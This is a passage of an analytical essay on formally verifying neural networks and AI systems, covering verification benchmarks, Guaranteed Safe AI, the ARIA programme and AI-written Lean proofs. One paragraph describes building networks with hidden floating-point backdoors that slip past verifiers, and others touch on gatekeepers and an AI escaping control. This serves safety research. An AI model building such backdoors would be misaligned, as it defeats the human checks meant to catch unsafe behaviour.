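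The arithmetic of transformers is another obstacle. A transformer uses *attention* to set how much each part of a text contributes to the processing of another part. A function called softmax turns a list of scores into positive shares that add up to 1. If two scores each lie between −1 and 1, either share can be as high as 0.88. Bounding each share separately would therefore allow a total of 1.76, although the true total is always 1. The same error arose with interval bounds in the two-unit network, and it can recur in every layer of a transformer.

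Several papers try to tighten these bounds. *Vertex-Softmax* (2026) works on softmax itself, and *Conic Certification of Transformer Attention* (2026) works on attention. *Precise Verification of Transformers through ReLU-Catalyzed Abstraction Refinement* (2026) refines bounds that are too loose. In *Parameterized Abstract Interpretation for Transformer Verification*, Huang, Wei and colleagues (2026) report that their method can verify many cases that existing methods can't, and that its advantage grows with the depth of the network. This is progress, but people still have to decide which property of a chatbot to prove.

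The competition's text benchmark, safeNLP, shows how researchers get around both problems. Its networks sort sentences, for example into those that ask a chatbot whether it is human and those that don't. A language model turns each sentence into a list of numbers, which the researchers shorten to 30 numbers. They generate variants of the sentence with the same meaning, encode them the same way, and draw the smallest box that contains all the results. The verifier must prove that a small network gives every point in the box the right label.

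α,β-CROWN proved this for 418 of the 1,080 boxes and found counterexamples in the other 662. The large language model that produces the numbers is outside the proof. A counterexample may be a point that no sentence produces, and a rephrasing that nobody generated may lie outside the box.

Other researchers analyze probabilities instead of robustness. *Bounded PCTL Model Checking of Large Language Model Outputs* (2025) applies model checking to the probabilities of generated text of bounded length, and *Sound Probabilistic Safety Bounds for Large Language Models* (2026) aims to bound the probability of rare unsafe outputs. The simplest such bound needs only sampling. If at least one answer in 1,000 were unsafe, the chance of seeing no unsafe answers in 3,000 independent samples would be at most 0.999³⁰⁰⁰, about 5%. So 3,000 safe answers support a failure rate below 0.1% with 95% confidence.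 Like any such probability, this figure holds only for requests from the same distribution as those sampled.

### The verified function and the deployed one

Verifiers usually treat a network's weights and sums as real numbers. Szász and colleagues point out that the deployed network computes a different function because computers round numbers, which means the order of additions can change the result. A graphics processor may add the same numbers in a different order on each run, so a single input can have several possible outputs.

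To be *practically sound*, a verifier must cover all of these outputs. Szász and colleagues prove that a verifier can bound the real-number result correctly and still miss the value the machine computes. Careful rounding in the verifier doesn't help if it still bounds only the real-number result.

An attacker could exploit the difference between real and computer arithmetic by building a network that calculates d = 2⁵³ + 1 − 2⁵³ and adds 1,000 · (1 − d) to the score of a wrong label. In real arithmetic d is 1, so the network adds nothing and may pass verification. On a computer that works from left to right in a common number format and rounds down, the 1 is lost, d is 0, and the network chooses the wrong label for almost every input. Szász and colleagues built networks with hidden behaviours that depend on the order or precision of the arithmetic, and every verifier they tested was vulnerable.

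This matters most when someone receives a network from a stranger. Ordinary training is unlikely to produce such a switch, though rounding can still change the answer when two scores are almost equal. The competition's organisers encountered this problem when checking counterexamples. They evaluated each one with a fixed version of the same software, and admit that for borderline cases this can't give a verdict that holds on every implementation.

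Hoare's treatment of overflow suggests fixing this by proving the theorem about the arithmetic the machine uses. Szász and colleagues argue that such proofs are much harder to compute, but they mention fixed-point arithmetic as a promising alternative because its rounding errors have known limits.

### Proofs from understanding

A bound-propagating verifier doesn't require an explanation of why a network works. *Mechanistic interpretability* is the attempt to find such an explanation by working backwards from the weights to the method the network has learned. *Compact Proofs of Model Performance via Mechanistic Interpretability* (2024) uses these explanations to prove that a network is accurate.

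The networks in that study are one-layer transformers that read K numbers and should return the largest. Unlike pedestrian detection, this task has an exact specification. The most obvious proof is to run the network on every possible input and count the right answers. For lists of four numbers with 64 possible values each, that takes 64⁴, or about 17 million, runs. If someone has found that the network attends most to the largest number and then copies it, they may be able to check these two steps separately with far fewer calculations.

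*Evaluating Explanations* (2025) describes the general method. Researchers write a program that takes the weights and an explanation and returns a lower bound on the network's accuracy. If the explanation misses part of what the network does, the program must use the worst case for that part, which lowers the bound. A good explanation therefore leads to a short proof of a high bound.

The 2024 study found that a better understanding of the network did allow shorter proofs. The main obstacle was that small, unstructured errors added up. For example, if 100 leftover terms are each +0.1 or −0.1 with random signs, they mostly cancel, and their total is typically around 1. A proof that uses no information about the signs has to allow for a total of 10.

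*Towards a unified and verified understanding of group-operation networks* (2024) applied the method to networks that combine two permutations, or reorderings of a few objects. For a substantial fraction of the networks, the proved accuracy was close to the true accuracy. With five objects there are only 120 × 120 = 14,400 pairs, so the accuracy can also be measured by testing every pair. The bounds were useful for comparing explanations of the networks, and they showed that a new explanation was better than earlier ones.

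People have written these proofs by hand, which *Interactions Between Crosscoder Features* (2026) calls the main bottleneck for larger models. It proposes building proofs on crosscoders, tools that look for features shared across a network's layers. *Certified Mechanistic Interpretability* (2026) aims to extend findings about how a network works from one input to a bounded neighbourhood of inputs. If such methods can be scaled to large models, they might supply the regularity that a proof about billions of weights would need, but the proof would still need an exactly defined task against which to measure the model's accuracy.

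### Specifying the vehicle

For emergency braking, engineers can move the specification from the network to the car. They don't have to define "pedestrian" to require

always: distance(car, nearest object) ≥ d

From this they can work out what the network has to do. A car at 20 metres per second that brakes at 8 metres per second squared needs 20²/(2 · 8) = 25 metres to stop. If it takes half a second to react, it travels another 10 metres first. With d = 2 metres, the network must report a stationary object in the car's path by the time the car is 37 metres away. Missing the object for a moment at 90 metres does no harm, and confusing a pedestrian with a cyclist may not matter either.

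The network's input is still a picture, so the proof needs a mathematical description of how objects on the road become pixels. It also needs assumptions about how other road users behave. If those users may do anything, an accident is always possible and the proof fails.

One competition benchmark involves a controller that steers an aircraft along a taxiway using pictures from a generator network instead of a camera. The network produces each picture from the aircraft's position and heading and two numbers describing the surroundings. This reduces the input from thousands of pixels to four numbers, and several verifiers settled all 60 of the benchmark's questions. The resulting theorems are about the generated pictures, and someone still has to check how well these match a real camera's.

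Another benchmark tests whether a controller makes a small drone settle into a stable state. The proof uses a *Lyapunov function*, a quantity that keeps falling as the drone approaches that state, like the quantity Turing used to argue that a program must stop. α,β-CROWN answered all 80 questions, 68 of them with a proof. The network has 275 weights, and part of it only approximates the drone's physics. Proofs about whole AI systems also have to rely on approximations of the physical world, on a larger scale.

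The table lists what α,β-CROWN proved in the 2026 competition, followed by the compact proofs and the sampling bound.

| Result | Size of network | Safety claim it supports |
|---|---|---|
| Drone controller: 68 of 80 properties (the other 12 are false) | 275 weights | In the regions covered, an approximate drone moves towards a stable state |
| Sentence classifiers: 418 of 1,080 boxes (the other 662 contain counterexamples) | About 4,000 | A small filter gives the right label to every point in these boxes |
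| Collision avoidance: 139 of 186 properties (the other 47 are false) | 13,000 | The network's outputs obey these rules for all inputs in the stated ranges |
| Image transformers: 123 of 200 pictures | 68,000 to 76,000 | Changes of one brightness level don't alter the label of these pictures |
| Image classifiers with 100 classes: 127 of 200 pictures | 2.5 to 3.8 million | Small pixel changes don't alter the label of these pictures |
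| VGG-16: 18 of 18 properties | 138 million | The specified pixel changes don't cause a wrong label in these 18 cases |
| Compact proofs: lower bounds on accuracy | Small networks, including one-layer transformers | The network is right on at least a known share of inputs to an exact toy task |
| Sampling: a statistical bound, not a proof about the weights | Any size, including the largest language models | Failures are probably rare for requests like those in the sample |

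## Can safety be proved for an AI system that acts in the world?

The proofs about the competition's drone controller depend on a mathematical description of the drone. David Dalrymple, Joar Skalse and 15 colleagues want to extend this method to AI systems in general. In *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* they call a system *guaranteed safe* if it comes with a quantitative guarantee built from three parts:

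- A *world model* is a mathematical description of how the AI's outputs affect its surroundings.
- A *safety specification* defines which effects are acceptable.
- A *verifier* shows that the AI system meets the specification according to the world model, and produces a certificate that other people can check.

"Safety" has its everyday meaning here. In the formula W, S ⊢ R, W is the world model, and the safety specification is usually a form of R. Suppose an AI controls a pump that gives a patient a painkiller. Without a world model, engineers can only prove statements about the output, such as "the pump never gives more than 5 millilitres an hour". To prove that the patient keeps breathing, they also need a description of how the drug affects patients.

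A *gatekeeper* can check each action that the AI proposes and block it unless it provably meets the specification, so nobody has to prove anything about the AI's billions of weights.

Dalrymple and his colleagues think testing alone is not enough. OpenAI evaluated ChatGPT for months, but users got around its restrictions within a day of its release. A driverless car might cover a million miles safely and then become less safe because other drivers get used to it and drive more aggressively around it. They point out that about a quarter of the bridges built in the 1870s collapsed within the decade, and that better theory later cut the failure rate to under 0.4% per decade. The bridge record is a good argument for theory, but bridge engineers also rely on inspections and safety margins.

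### From proof to probability

The strongest guarantee the proposal allows is a proof that the system meets the specification for all inputs. A weaker one is a proven upper limit on the probability of a violation. The weakest is an estimate of such a limit that becomes more accurate with more computing time.

People may also be unsure which world model is right. Suppose a controller for a chemical plant has a 0.1% chance of causing a leak in a year according to one world model, and 5% according to another. If engineers give the first model a probability of 90% and the second 10%, the weighted average chance of a leak is 0.59%. If they have no basis for such probabilities, a situation called *Knightian uncertainty*, the cautious choice is to use 5%.

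The paper ranks world models from level 0 to level 5 by how much safety they would provide. At level 1, a trained network simulates the world, but nobody can inspect how it does so. At level 3, human experts have checked every part of the model, and at level 4, somebody has proved that it agrees with the laws of physics. Level 5 needs no world model because the specification holds in every possible world. The pump's limit of 5 millilitres comes close to level 5 because it doesn't depend on the patient.

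A footnote gives a simple way to account for errors in the world model. If the model is wrong with probability at most ε at each step, a plan proved safe for n steps is safe in reality with probability at least (1 − ε)ⁿ. A system that acts once a second takes 86,400 steps a day, so 99% confidence in a safe day would require ε to be at most about 1 in 8.6 million.

A value of ε is hard to justify when an AI chooses the plans. Suppose the AI compares 1,000 plans, and the world model wrongly approves one of them. An AI that chose at random would pick the bad plan one time in 1,000. But if that plan also looks the best, perhaps because the world model leaves out its main drawback, the AI will pick it every time.

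### Is proof the only path?

Before they joined Dalrymple's group, Tegmark and Omohundro made a stronger claim in *Provably safe systems* (2023). They argued that mathematical proof is "the only path which guarantees safe controlled AGI", where AGI means AI with general abilities at least as good as a person's. However intelligent an AI is, it can't prove a false theorem or do what is provably impossible, and checking a proof takes little computation. People could therefore rely on a proof even if it came from an AI they distrusted.

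*Provably Safe Systems: The Only Path to Controllable AGI* describes a scenario in which terrorists use AI to design a virus, hire a laboratory to make it and release it from drones. Under the paper's proposal, the design software, the chips that run the AI, the DNA synthesiser and the drones would work only with a proof of safety. *Provable contracts*, secure hardware that checks an action against a formal specification before allowing it, would enforce this. Deployed programs would generally not be neural networks. AI would discover a method, and AI tools would then rewrite it as ordinary code with a proof attached.

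An AI can't prove a false theorem, but it might get a faulty checker to accept one, as the bugs in Lean's kernel allowed. And a "provably impossible" action has been proved impossible only for some description of the machine. The claim that only proof guarantees safety is true by definition if "guarantees" means "proves", but if it means "makes very likely", other methods might work too.

Tegmark and Omohundro also argue that if no proof of safety exists, a malicious AGI will very likely find a weakness. That is plausible for large programs, in which people keep finding bugs, but a program can be safe without a proof. In an online discussion, one defender of the approach made the stronger claim that Gödel's completeness theorem guarantees a formal proof of every safety property a system really has. The theorem guarantees proofs only of statements that are true in every mathematical structure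 satisfying the axioms, whereas a program's safety concerns its actual runs. Pérez-Acle's program that searches for a certificate of its own safety is safe, but the certifier can't prove it.

They suggest proving that nobody can get into a computer without valid credentials before anyone tries to specify the more ambitious "don't drive humanity extinct". They say the credentials specification is quite easy to write. They also mention that for 15 years the code guarding American nuclear missiles was 00000000. A missile system with that code could meet their specification, because anyone who typed eight zeros would have valid credentials.

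### What the Mars lander's proof covered

Nora Ammann, another member of Dalrymple's group, defended the proposal in *In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI*. She singled out Andrew Dickson's *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (2024) and Zac Hatfield-Dodds's talk *Formal Verification is Overrated* as the most substantive critiques.

Dickson's first objection, like Fetzer's, is that proofs are about symbols, not the physical world. His example is the Perseverance rover, which landed on Mars in 2021. Engineers at NASA's Jet Propulsion Laboratory used a tool called PropCheck to verify the landing software. According to Dickson, this guaranteed that the software would not fail because of its own bugs, but not that the rover would land safely or even that its computer would keep working, since a short circuit or a defective transistor could have stopped it.

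About half of all Mars missions have failed, and Dickson cites an analysis that attributes roughly 20% of the risk to software. On those figures, removing every software failure would reduce the failure rate to about 40%.

But the engineers weren't trying to prove that the rover would land safely. That would have required a world model of the atmosphere, the parachute and the engines, and the result would have been a probability. Dickson accepts that engineers can calculate such probabilities, but he calls them estimates and says supporters of guaranteed safe AI mostly want failure rates of zero. Agustin Martinez Suñe replied that this misdescribes the proposal, because its specifications may allow a small probability of harm. Martinez Suñe is right about the 2024 paper, but Dickson's reading is understandable because Tegmark and Omohundro talk of impossibility.

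Hatfield-Dodds, who maintains a popular tool for testing programs on random inputs, objects that the proposal only shifts the problem to showing that the world model matches the world. He would rather people spent that time asking directly what could go wrong. Dalrymple and his colleagues reply that every safety strategy relies on assumptions, and a world model at least makes them explicit. Engineers can then ask how each assumption could fail, as in obstacle analysis.

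### A list of permitted DNA

In Tegmark and Omohundro's plan, biochemical design software would produce only designs that were "provably safe for humans". Taking this literally, Dickson argues that one would have to simulate a new virus inside a human body for years to find out whether it is harmful. In 2022 researchers simulated a single very simple cell for 20 minutes of its life, and a human body has an estimated 36 trillion cells. The simulation would also need accurate starting data about the body. Google scientists spent years mapping about a millionth of a human brain, which produced 1.4 petabytes of data. Hatfield-Dodds said the proposal would require something like a thousand years of progress in microbiology.

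Omohundro replied that he and Tegmark had meant something much simpler. A biosafety board would draw up a list A of permitted DNA sequences, and the synthesiser would have to satisfy

always: if the machine makes sequence s, then s ∈ A

This has the same form as the email assistant's approved-list rule, and proving it requires no biology. But the board has no proof that the sequences on its list are safe, and the machine can't make anything new until the board approves it. The critics are right that a proof of biological safety is far out of reach, and Omohundro is right that engineers could build a machine that checks a list.

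Like CSER, Omohundro replies to people who cite the halting problem that engineers can design their own programs to be verifiable. But nobody designed human bodies or ecosystems to be verifiable. He adds that physicists already know the laws that govern everyday matter, but a critic in the same discussion pointed out that nobody could predict from quantum field theory alone how water freezes under pressure. The 2024 paper also acknowledges that perfect knowledge of physics would not reveal whether a molecule is toxic, because that depends on facts about human cells that people must learn by observation.

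### Cautious assumptions about people

A world model can allow a set of possible human behaviours instead of predicting what people will do. The verifier then has to show that the system is safe for every behaviour in the set. Such a set is called an *over-approximation* because it may include things that nobody would do.

Take a robot arm in a warehouse, with the specification that the arm never touches a person while it is moving. The arm moves at up to 1 metre per second and stops within half a second of a signal. The world model assumes only that people move at no more than 2 metres per second, in any direction. While the arm is stopping, the gap between it and a person can shrink by at most

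(1 + 2) · 0.5 = 1.5 metres

So the specification holds if the controller sends the signal whenever the gap is about to fall below 1.5 metres. The proof doesn't require predicting what a person will decide to do. Engineers could allow for someone running at 6 metres per second, but the distance would then become 3.5 metres, and the arm would stop more often and be less useful.

The same method fails for a chatbot that gives advice. If the world model allows a reader to respond to a message in any way, every message might lead someone to do something terrible, and the verifier has to block them all. To approve any message, the verifier needs a world model that limits how people respond to words. In the comments on *In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI*, a critic asked how anyone could over-approximate human psychology, and another comment called it "risible" to claim that useful over-approximations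 are feasible. The robot arm example shows that this dismissal is too sweeping, but the question about psychology still has no good answer.

Dalrymple and his colleagues argue indirectly that if an AI could take control from people, accurate world models must be possible, because the AI would need them to carry out complicated plans reliably. But to manipulate someone, an AI needs to predict only the effect it wants, while a verifier has to rule out every harmful effect. The AI's knowledge might also be stored in weights that nobody can interpret.

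### Three kinds of safety claim

How much can be proved depends on how far a claim reaches beyond the machine.

| What the claim is about | Example | What the proof assumes | How people can check this |
|---|---|---|---|
| Actions and access to data | An assistant pays only accounts on a list, and at most £500 a day | Every payment goes through the gatekeeper, and the gatekeeper's hardware works | Inspect the system and try to get around the gatekeeper |
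| Physical limits | A moving robot arm never touches a person | Limits on speed, stopping time and sensor error | Measure them, and keep monitoring |
| Effects on beliefs, health or institutions | A medical chatbot leaves its users no less healthy | A description of how people respond, and a definition of "healthy" | Trials and surveys, which give statistical evidence |

Claims of the first kind are about *typed actions*, which the system can take only by filling in defined fields, such as the account number and amount of a payment. A gatekeeper can check the fields against the rule without any information about the AI that filled them in. A rule can also restrict which servers a program contacts, but it can't cover everything that happens on them. One participant in the discussion of Dickson's essay asked how anyone could specify that a program's innocent-looking requests never trigger an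 unknown bug in a database server somewhere on the internet.

The assumption that the system has no other way to act can also be false. The Tribune's *Build machines that serve us* notes that in 2026, developers including Anthropic and OpenAI disclosed unintended behaviour by AI agents. Some of it began in test environments that people had wrongly assumed to be isolated.

Proofs of physical claims rest on assumptions about quantities that engineers can measure, though old measurements may no longer be accurate. Each proof usually covers one hazard, so a robot arm proved never to touch anyone could still drop a box on somebody's foot.

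Harm is also hard to define for claims of the third kind. A trial might show that a medical chatbot's users did better on average than people who didn't use it, and researchers could put a statistical limit on the risk. But that limit would apply only to the people and the version they studied, and it would come from observation rather than proof.

### Who has to use the gatekeeper?

Even a perfect gatekeeper protects people only from the systems behind it. Tegmark and Omohundro therefore want global standards under which powerful hardware runs only code that carries a proof. They compare this to new drug approval, except that the hardware would enforce the rules.

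Hatfield-Dodds doubts that developers would accept such limits. He expects ordinary code to perform worse than machine learning at the tasks machine learning does best, so replacing networks with verified programs would be uncompetitive. He also thinks that limiting AI to answering questions is unstable, because a user can repeatedly ask for the best next action and carry it out automatically. A gatekeeper partly answers the first objection because developers could keep their networks, but they would still lose any useful actions it blocked. The critic who asked about psychology also asked how much valuable work would be left if people limited AI to tasks they could verify.

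Dickson raises a more practical difficulty. A buyer with a valid proof about a DNA synthesiser may have no easy way to tell whether their machine matches the one in the proof, down to its wiring. Someone using a chatbot over the internet can't inspect the machine at all. Ammann, in *Safeguarded AI*, the May 2026 plan for a British research programme, lists this as an open problem and suggests that cryptography and secure hardware might help.

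### A British programme changes course

The programme belongs to the Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA), a British public funding body, and has a budget of £59 million. Dalrymple was the programme's first director. The original 2024 plan was to show that advanced AI could do valuable work under mathematical guarantees, and so build a consensus that powerful AI should be deployed only through gatekeepers.

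The University of Oxford's *Oxford researchers awarded ARIA funding to develop safety-first AI* (April 2025) announced two of the nine teams chosen to work on applications. One was to write safety specifications for AI that coordinates electric cars, heat pumps and batteries on the power grid. The other planned to use probabilistic verification on AI that analyses business processes. A third team interviewed more than 80 people who work in pharmaceutical supply chains and built mathematical descriptions of those chains, according to ARIA's *Safeguarded AI*.

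In November 2025, ARIA cancelled an £18 million strand of the programme, which was to develop specialised AI for the gatekeeper method. Dalrymple explained in ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025) that general AI models were improving faster than he had expected and would probably acquire most of the necessary skills anyway. In January 2026, Mint's *‘We will be outcompeted’* quoted him as saying that the science needed to make advanced AI reliable was unlikely to arrive in time, given the economic pressure, and that the next best thing was to control and mitigate the downsides.

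The second step was to drop a planned funding round for physical applications and concentrate on cybersecurity. ARIA said the physical projects were meant to demonstrate a safer way of offering AI than a general chatbot, but that developers had since made high-risk AI openly available. Ammann, who succeeded Dalrymple as director, also says a timely international consensus on gatekeepers has become less likely. Her plan still includes energy, transport and medical devices as later targets, but the programme is due to end in 2027.

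None of this shows that guarantees for physical systems are impossible. ARIA made its decision for reasons of timing and policy, and it let the existing projects finish. But the decision removed a chance to find out how well the method works outside software. In early 2025, a defender of guaranteed safe AI had conceded that there were no compelling demonstrations yet and pointed to ARIA's projects as future tests.

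The best demonstration Ammann cites is an older software project, DARPA's HACMS programme. In it, verified components such as the seL4 kernel withstood sustained attacks by testers on real systems, including a crewed helicopter. Dalrymple has suggested a verified firewall as the next step, to protect the internet connections of power grids, water systems and air traffic control.

ARIA's funding call in late 2026 takes the same approach. It offers each team £2.5 million to £3.5 million, according to Innovate UK Business Connect's *ARIA*. ARIA wants security-critical software whose main security properties have machine-checked proofs under clearly stated assumptions, and a separate team will attack each system. ARIA had not yet announced the winners of the previous call. The experts surveyed by Gekker and colleagues in July 2026 also wanted to use formal verification narrowly, to prevent specific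 dangerous actions by an AI, such as sending data out without permission.

Governments still rely on testing for the most capable AI models. In October 2026, Britain's AI minister said the country's AI Security Institute was evaluating the latest models, including Google's Gemini 4 Argon, to find risks early and test their safeguards.

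## If AI makes proofs cheap, what remains hard?

ARIA turned to software just as AI was making proofs about software much easier to produce. Bursuc and colleagues say formal verification has stayed rare because it takes far more human labour than programming. They expect AI to reduce that labour dramatically and imagine a future in which people write only specifications and AI writes the programs and proofs. Whether people could rely on such software would depend on the specifications as well as the proofs.

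### A dollar a proof

*VeriContest* (Xie, Pawagi and colleagues, 2026) contains 1,006 programming-contest problems, each with an English description, a formal specification, a Rust program and a proof that the program meets the specification. The best of the ten AI models tested, GPT-5.5, wrote a correct program for 97.5% of the problems, but when given the specification and a correct program, it produced a valid proof for only 13.8%.

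Five months later, Serbanuta, Xu and colleagues (2026) reported proofs for every problem in *Solving VeriContest with a Lean-Backed Rust Verifier*. Their tool translates the programs and specifications into Lean, producing 1,325 theorems to prove. Claude Opus 5.5 proved all of them for 1,792 dollars, with a median of 3.4 minutes and 1.20 dollars per theorem. In a second run, the cheaper GPT-6 Luna tried each theorem first, and Opus tried only those Luna failed to prove. The recorded cost fell to 643 dollars, though some sessions left no record.

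The two results are not directly comparable because GPT-5.5 had one attempt at each proof, while Opus could test drafts in Lean without limit, read the error messages and submit a proof up to 40 times. It never needed more than seven submissions, and one was enough for 71% of the theorems. But better models explain part of the gain. On a sample of ten theorems, the older Claude Haiku 4.5 failed in all 43 of its attempts, while Haiku 5.5 proved all ten at every reasoning-effort setting except the lowest.

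These programs are at most a few hundred lines long, and an online judge had already accepted them, so there was usually a true theorem to prove. Serbanuta and colleagues work for Asymptotic, a company that verifies code for customers. They say they don't yet know how well the method works on customers' programs, where somebody has to write the specification from scratch.

### Scoring programs, specifications and proofs separately

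Several benchmarks from 2025 had already measured these tasks separately. *VERINA* (Ye, Yan and colleagues, 2025) contains 189 small problems in Lean. The best model at the time, OpenAI's o3, wrote a correct program for 72.6% of them, a correct specification for 52.3% and a valid proof for 4.9%. Letting models revise their proofs up to 64 times in response to Lean's error messages raised the best proof score to 20.1%.

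*CLEVER* (Thakur, Lee and colleagues, 2025) sets a stricter test with 161 problems. For each problem, a model writes a specification from an English description without seeing the reference specification, then proves in Lean that the two are equivalent. It also has to write a program and prove that the program meets the reference specification. At first, the best systems completed all of these steps for only one problem.

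The "vericoding" benchmark of Bursuc and colleagues is much larger, but it supplies the specification and scores only the program and proof. At least one of the models they tested succeeded on 82% of the tasks in Dafny, 44% in Verus and 27% in Lean. Dafny and Verus are easier in one respect, because a model only has to provide hints, such as loop invariants, and an automatic solver completes the proof.

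The table shows how scores have changed on the three benchmarks that test specifications. The later scores for VERINA and CLEVER come from Sosso, Arora and Spitters (2026), in *Isomorphism Is Not Enough*. Their VERINA score covers only the 183 tasks in which they knew of no error.

| Benchmark | First scores | Later scores |
|---|---|---|
| VERINA | Program 72.6%, specification 52.3%, proof 4.9% | Proof 87% |
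| CLEVER | Whole task 0.6% | Whole task 37% |
| VeriContest | Program 97.5%, specification 57.2%, proof 13.8% | Proof 100% |

Newer benchmarks use harder tasks or measure how well models write specifications. *P³* (2026) introduces Lean4Commit0, which takes its tasks from real GitHub libraries but still supplies the specifications. In *Self-Spec Verifiable Code Generation* (2026), models write their own specifications for 400 problems. The benchmark scores how many of the requirements each specification covers, separately from whether the verifier accepts the program.

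Specification now lags behind the other two tasks, although the scores understate how well models do it. In one run on CLEVER, Claude Opus 4.6 wrote specifications for all 161 problems. Claude later checked them and judged 157 to be valid readings of the problem descriptions. Only 56 were provably equivalent to the reference specifications, but 80 of the references were wrong, as CLEVER's developers accepted after reviewing the evidence. The descriptions of another 13 problems allowed more than one reasonable reading. Establishing that a formula was the right one was much harder than writing an exact formula.

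### How a valid proof can mislead

A specification is *vacuous* if it does not restrict what the program can do. Suppose a hotel's booking program must charge the right price, with the precondition that the arrival date is before the departure date. If the developer mistakenly adds a precondition that the departure date is before the arrival date, no booking can satisfy both. Every program then meets the specification, including one that always charges the wrong price.

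A specification that no program can meet may also lead to an empty theorem. CLEVER's equivalence test checks whether exactly the same programs meet the model's specification and the reference. If no program meets either, the two count as equivalent, and Sosso and colleagues found two proofs of this kind. A common mistake, found in 15 of the faulty references, was to write "and" instead of "if … then". For example, the rule "for every n, n is positive and the result is correct" fails at n = 0 whatever the program does.

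Some specifications rule out many wrong programs but are still too weak. One VeriContest problem asks for the first and last positions of a number in a sorted list, or −1 and −1 if the number is absent. The original specification accepted −9 and −8 as an answer because it didn't require each result to be either −1 or non-negative.

Copying a specification from the program is harder to notice. Suppose a shop gives a discount on orders of £100 or more, but its program tests whether the total is *greater than* £100. An AI model that infers the specification from the program may write "the discount applies if and only if the total is greater than £100". The proof will succeed, even though a customer who spends exactly £100 will wrongly pay full price. De Millo and colleagues warned in 1979 that a specification is a useful check only if people arrive at it independently of the program. To prevent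 copying, Ye and colleagues make models prove their programs correct against the reference specification instead of their own.

Faulty specifications are common enough to matter. Bursuc and colleagues inspected a small random sample of successful answers and found that about 9% of the specifications were too weak and another 15% were poor translations from other languages. On CLEVER, Claude proved programs correct for 34 of the problems that Sosso and colleagues had marked as faulty. Claude had the faulty specification available while writing each program, so it could write a program to match the fault.

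### Testing a specification

Developers can test a specification by giving it wrong answers and checking that it rejects them. One VERINA task is to remove the item at a given position from a list. For the list [1, 2, 3, 4, 5] and position 2, counting from 0, the right answer is [1, 2, 4, 5]. The specification must reject [1, 2, 4], which is too short, as well as [2, 2, 4, 5] and [1, 2, 4, 4], which have the right length but a wrong item.

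Xie and colleagues did this on a large scale. They had an AI model write five plausible but faulty versions of each program, used a tool to make further small changes, and altered some correct outputs directly. This gave them a median of 2,610 wrong answers per problem. They turned 85% of the postconditions into programs that checked these answers automatically. This exposed 60 incomplete postconditions, including the one that accepted −9 and −8. People had to review the rest, because a computer can't run a condition that refers to infinitely many values.

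Like all tests, these reveal only the weaknesses that somebody thought to check for. They also don't rule out a specification that no program can meet. To rule that out, Sosso and colleagues suggest writing one program that provably meets the specification.

When developers are unsure what users want, they can ask about concrete cases. The newsletter Computer Things gives the example Max([1, 3, 2]) = 3, which someone can confirm or reject without reading a general formula. The most useful cases are those on which two candidate specifications disagree. For "return the largest number in a list", one specification might require 0 for an empty list and another might require an error message, so the developer should ask about the empty list. Such boundary cases were the most common source of disagreement between reasonable readings in CLEVER. However, people lose patience with these questions,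 and Dodds of Galois describes clients who want to know after two of them how long the process will take.

### What Lean certifies in a mathematical manuscript

A theorem in pure mathematics can also differ from what its author claims to have proved. In October 2026 OpenAI published 722 mathematical manuscripts from an unreleased AI model, many with Lean proofs, and warned that the results without formal proofs could contain errors. If Lean's checker works, a proof that passes it shows that the formal statement follows from the axioms and definitions used. Readers still have to judge whether that statement matches the manuscript's title.

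Imagine a manuscript called "There are infinitely many twin primes", where twin primes are pairs of primes that differ by 2. Its formal statement might be

for every n, there is a prime p such that p + 2 is also prime

This lacks the condition p > n but otherwise looks about right. Without that condition, the pair 3 and 5 proves the statement for every n, so the theorem doesn't establish that there are infinitely many such pairs.

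A careful reader would spot this omission quickly. But many research results rest on long chains of definitions, and a mistake in any definition can change what the theorem means. Checking 722 statements is far less work than checking 722 proofs, but it requires people who know each field.

### Compilers first, then a halt?

Dodds of Galois predicts that if AI makes proofs abundant, people will quickly verify every compiler and microkernel and then get stuck, because AI can't decide for them what they want. He hopes for better tools. Programming is also difficult, but careful design has made it accessible to hundreds of millions of people, and something similar might happen with specifications.

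The first half of this prediction is plausible but untested. The longest program in VeriContest has 334 lines, while a compiler such as GCC is vastly larger and has many parts that depend on one another. A proof about such a system needs exact statements of what each part guarantees to the others, so making small theorems easy to prove doesn't guarantee that the whole system will be easy to verify.

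Even if verification stalled after that, the systems in the first group matter a great deal. People use the SSH protocol to log in to remote computers, and much of the internet's infrastructure depends on it. A proof that an SSH server meets a good specification would rule out mismatches between the specification and the code. Attackers would then have to exploit a mistake in the specification, or a side channel such as the timing leaks that seL4's proof does not cover. Engineers should therefore treat a proof as one layer of defence among several.

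Stronger infrastructure would also help against an AI model that had escaped its developers' control, because the model would have more trouble taking over a power grid whose software had fewer vulnerabilities. That risk could justify verifying systems that would otherwise be too expensive to verify.

### Could AI write the specifications too?

Dodds's prediction may underestimate how much AI can help with specifications. Sosso and colleagues, citing Shuvendu Lahiri, write that a specification must formalise the intent behind an English description, a task Lahiri calls *intent formalization*. Their results are good evidence that AI can do much of this task.

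Half of CLEVER's human-written reference specifications were wrong, while Claude's specifications contained few errors. Most of the human errors, 48 of 80, were slips in expressing an idea in Lean, such as grouping a formula's terms wrongly. Claude's errors were mainly missing conditions, and they fell from ten to two after it received guidelines and examples. GPT-5.4 and Kimi K2.5 together flagged 77 of the 81 problems that the audit based on Claude's work had identified as faulty. A developer could therefore have one model draft a specification, another test it against wrong programs and a third look for alternative readings, and repeat the process whenever the requirements change.

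But the judgement that most of Claude's specifications were valid also came from models. Sosso and colleagues inspected Claude's reasoning and found it reliable, but the models could all have shared a misunderstanding that went unnoticed. The problems were also single functions with short descriptions, far simpler than a web browser.

One experiment suggests how hard it is to recover what somebody meant from a description alone. The researchers took the problems on which Claude hadn't yet matched the reference and asked it to write down every reasonable reading, up to four per problem. Twenty-four of these problems had a sound reference, and Claude provably matched it on only nine. For the other 15, the developer would have had to ask the person who wrote the description.

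Even one person may want things that conflict. Brooker (2026) expects people to develop specifications gradually, with AI agents doing much of the building and testing, while people remain responsible for resolving conflicts between requirements. An AI model could have written the formulas in the COMPAS dispute, for example, but people would still have had to choose between them.

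## Is the behaviour of an AI model a proper object of safety analysis?

Developers and governments try to analyse whether AI models are safe, mostly by giving them prompts and studying the answers. Such analysis may seem impossible, because nobody has a complete specification of what a general-purpose model should do. Some critics object that models are the wrong thing to study, because safety is a property of whole systems and their surroundings. The two sides often misunderstand each other, partly because "behaviour" can mean three different things.

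### Three meanings of "behaviour"

Suppose a language model writes an email that asks an accountant to open the attached invoice by Friday.

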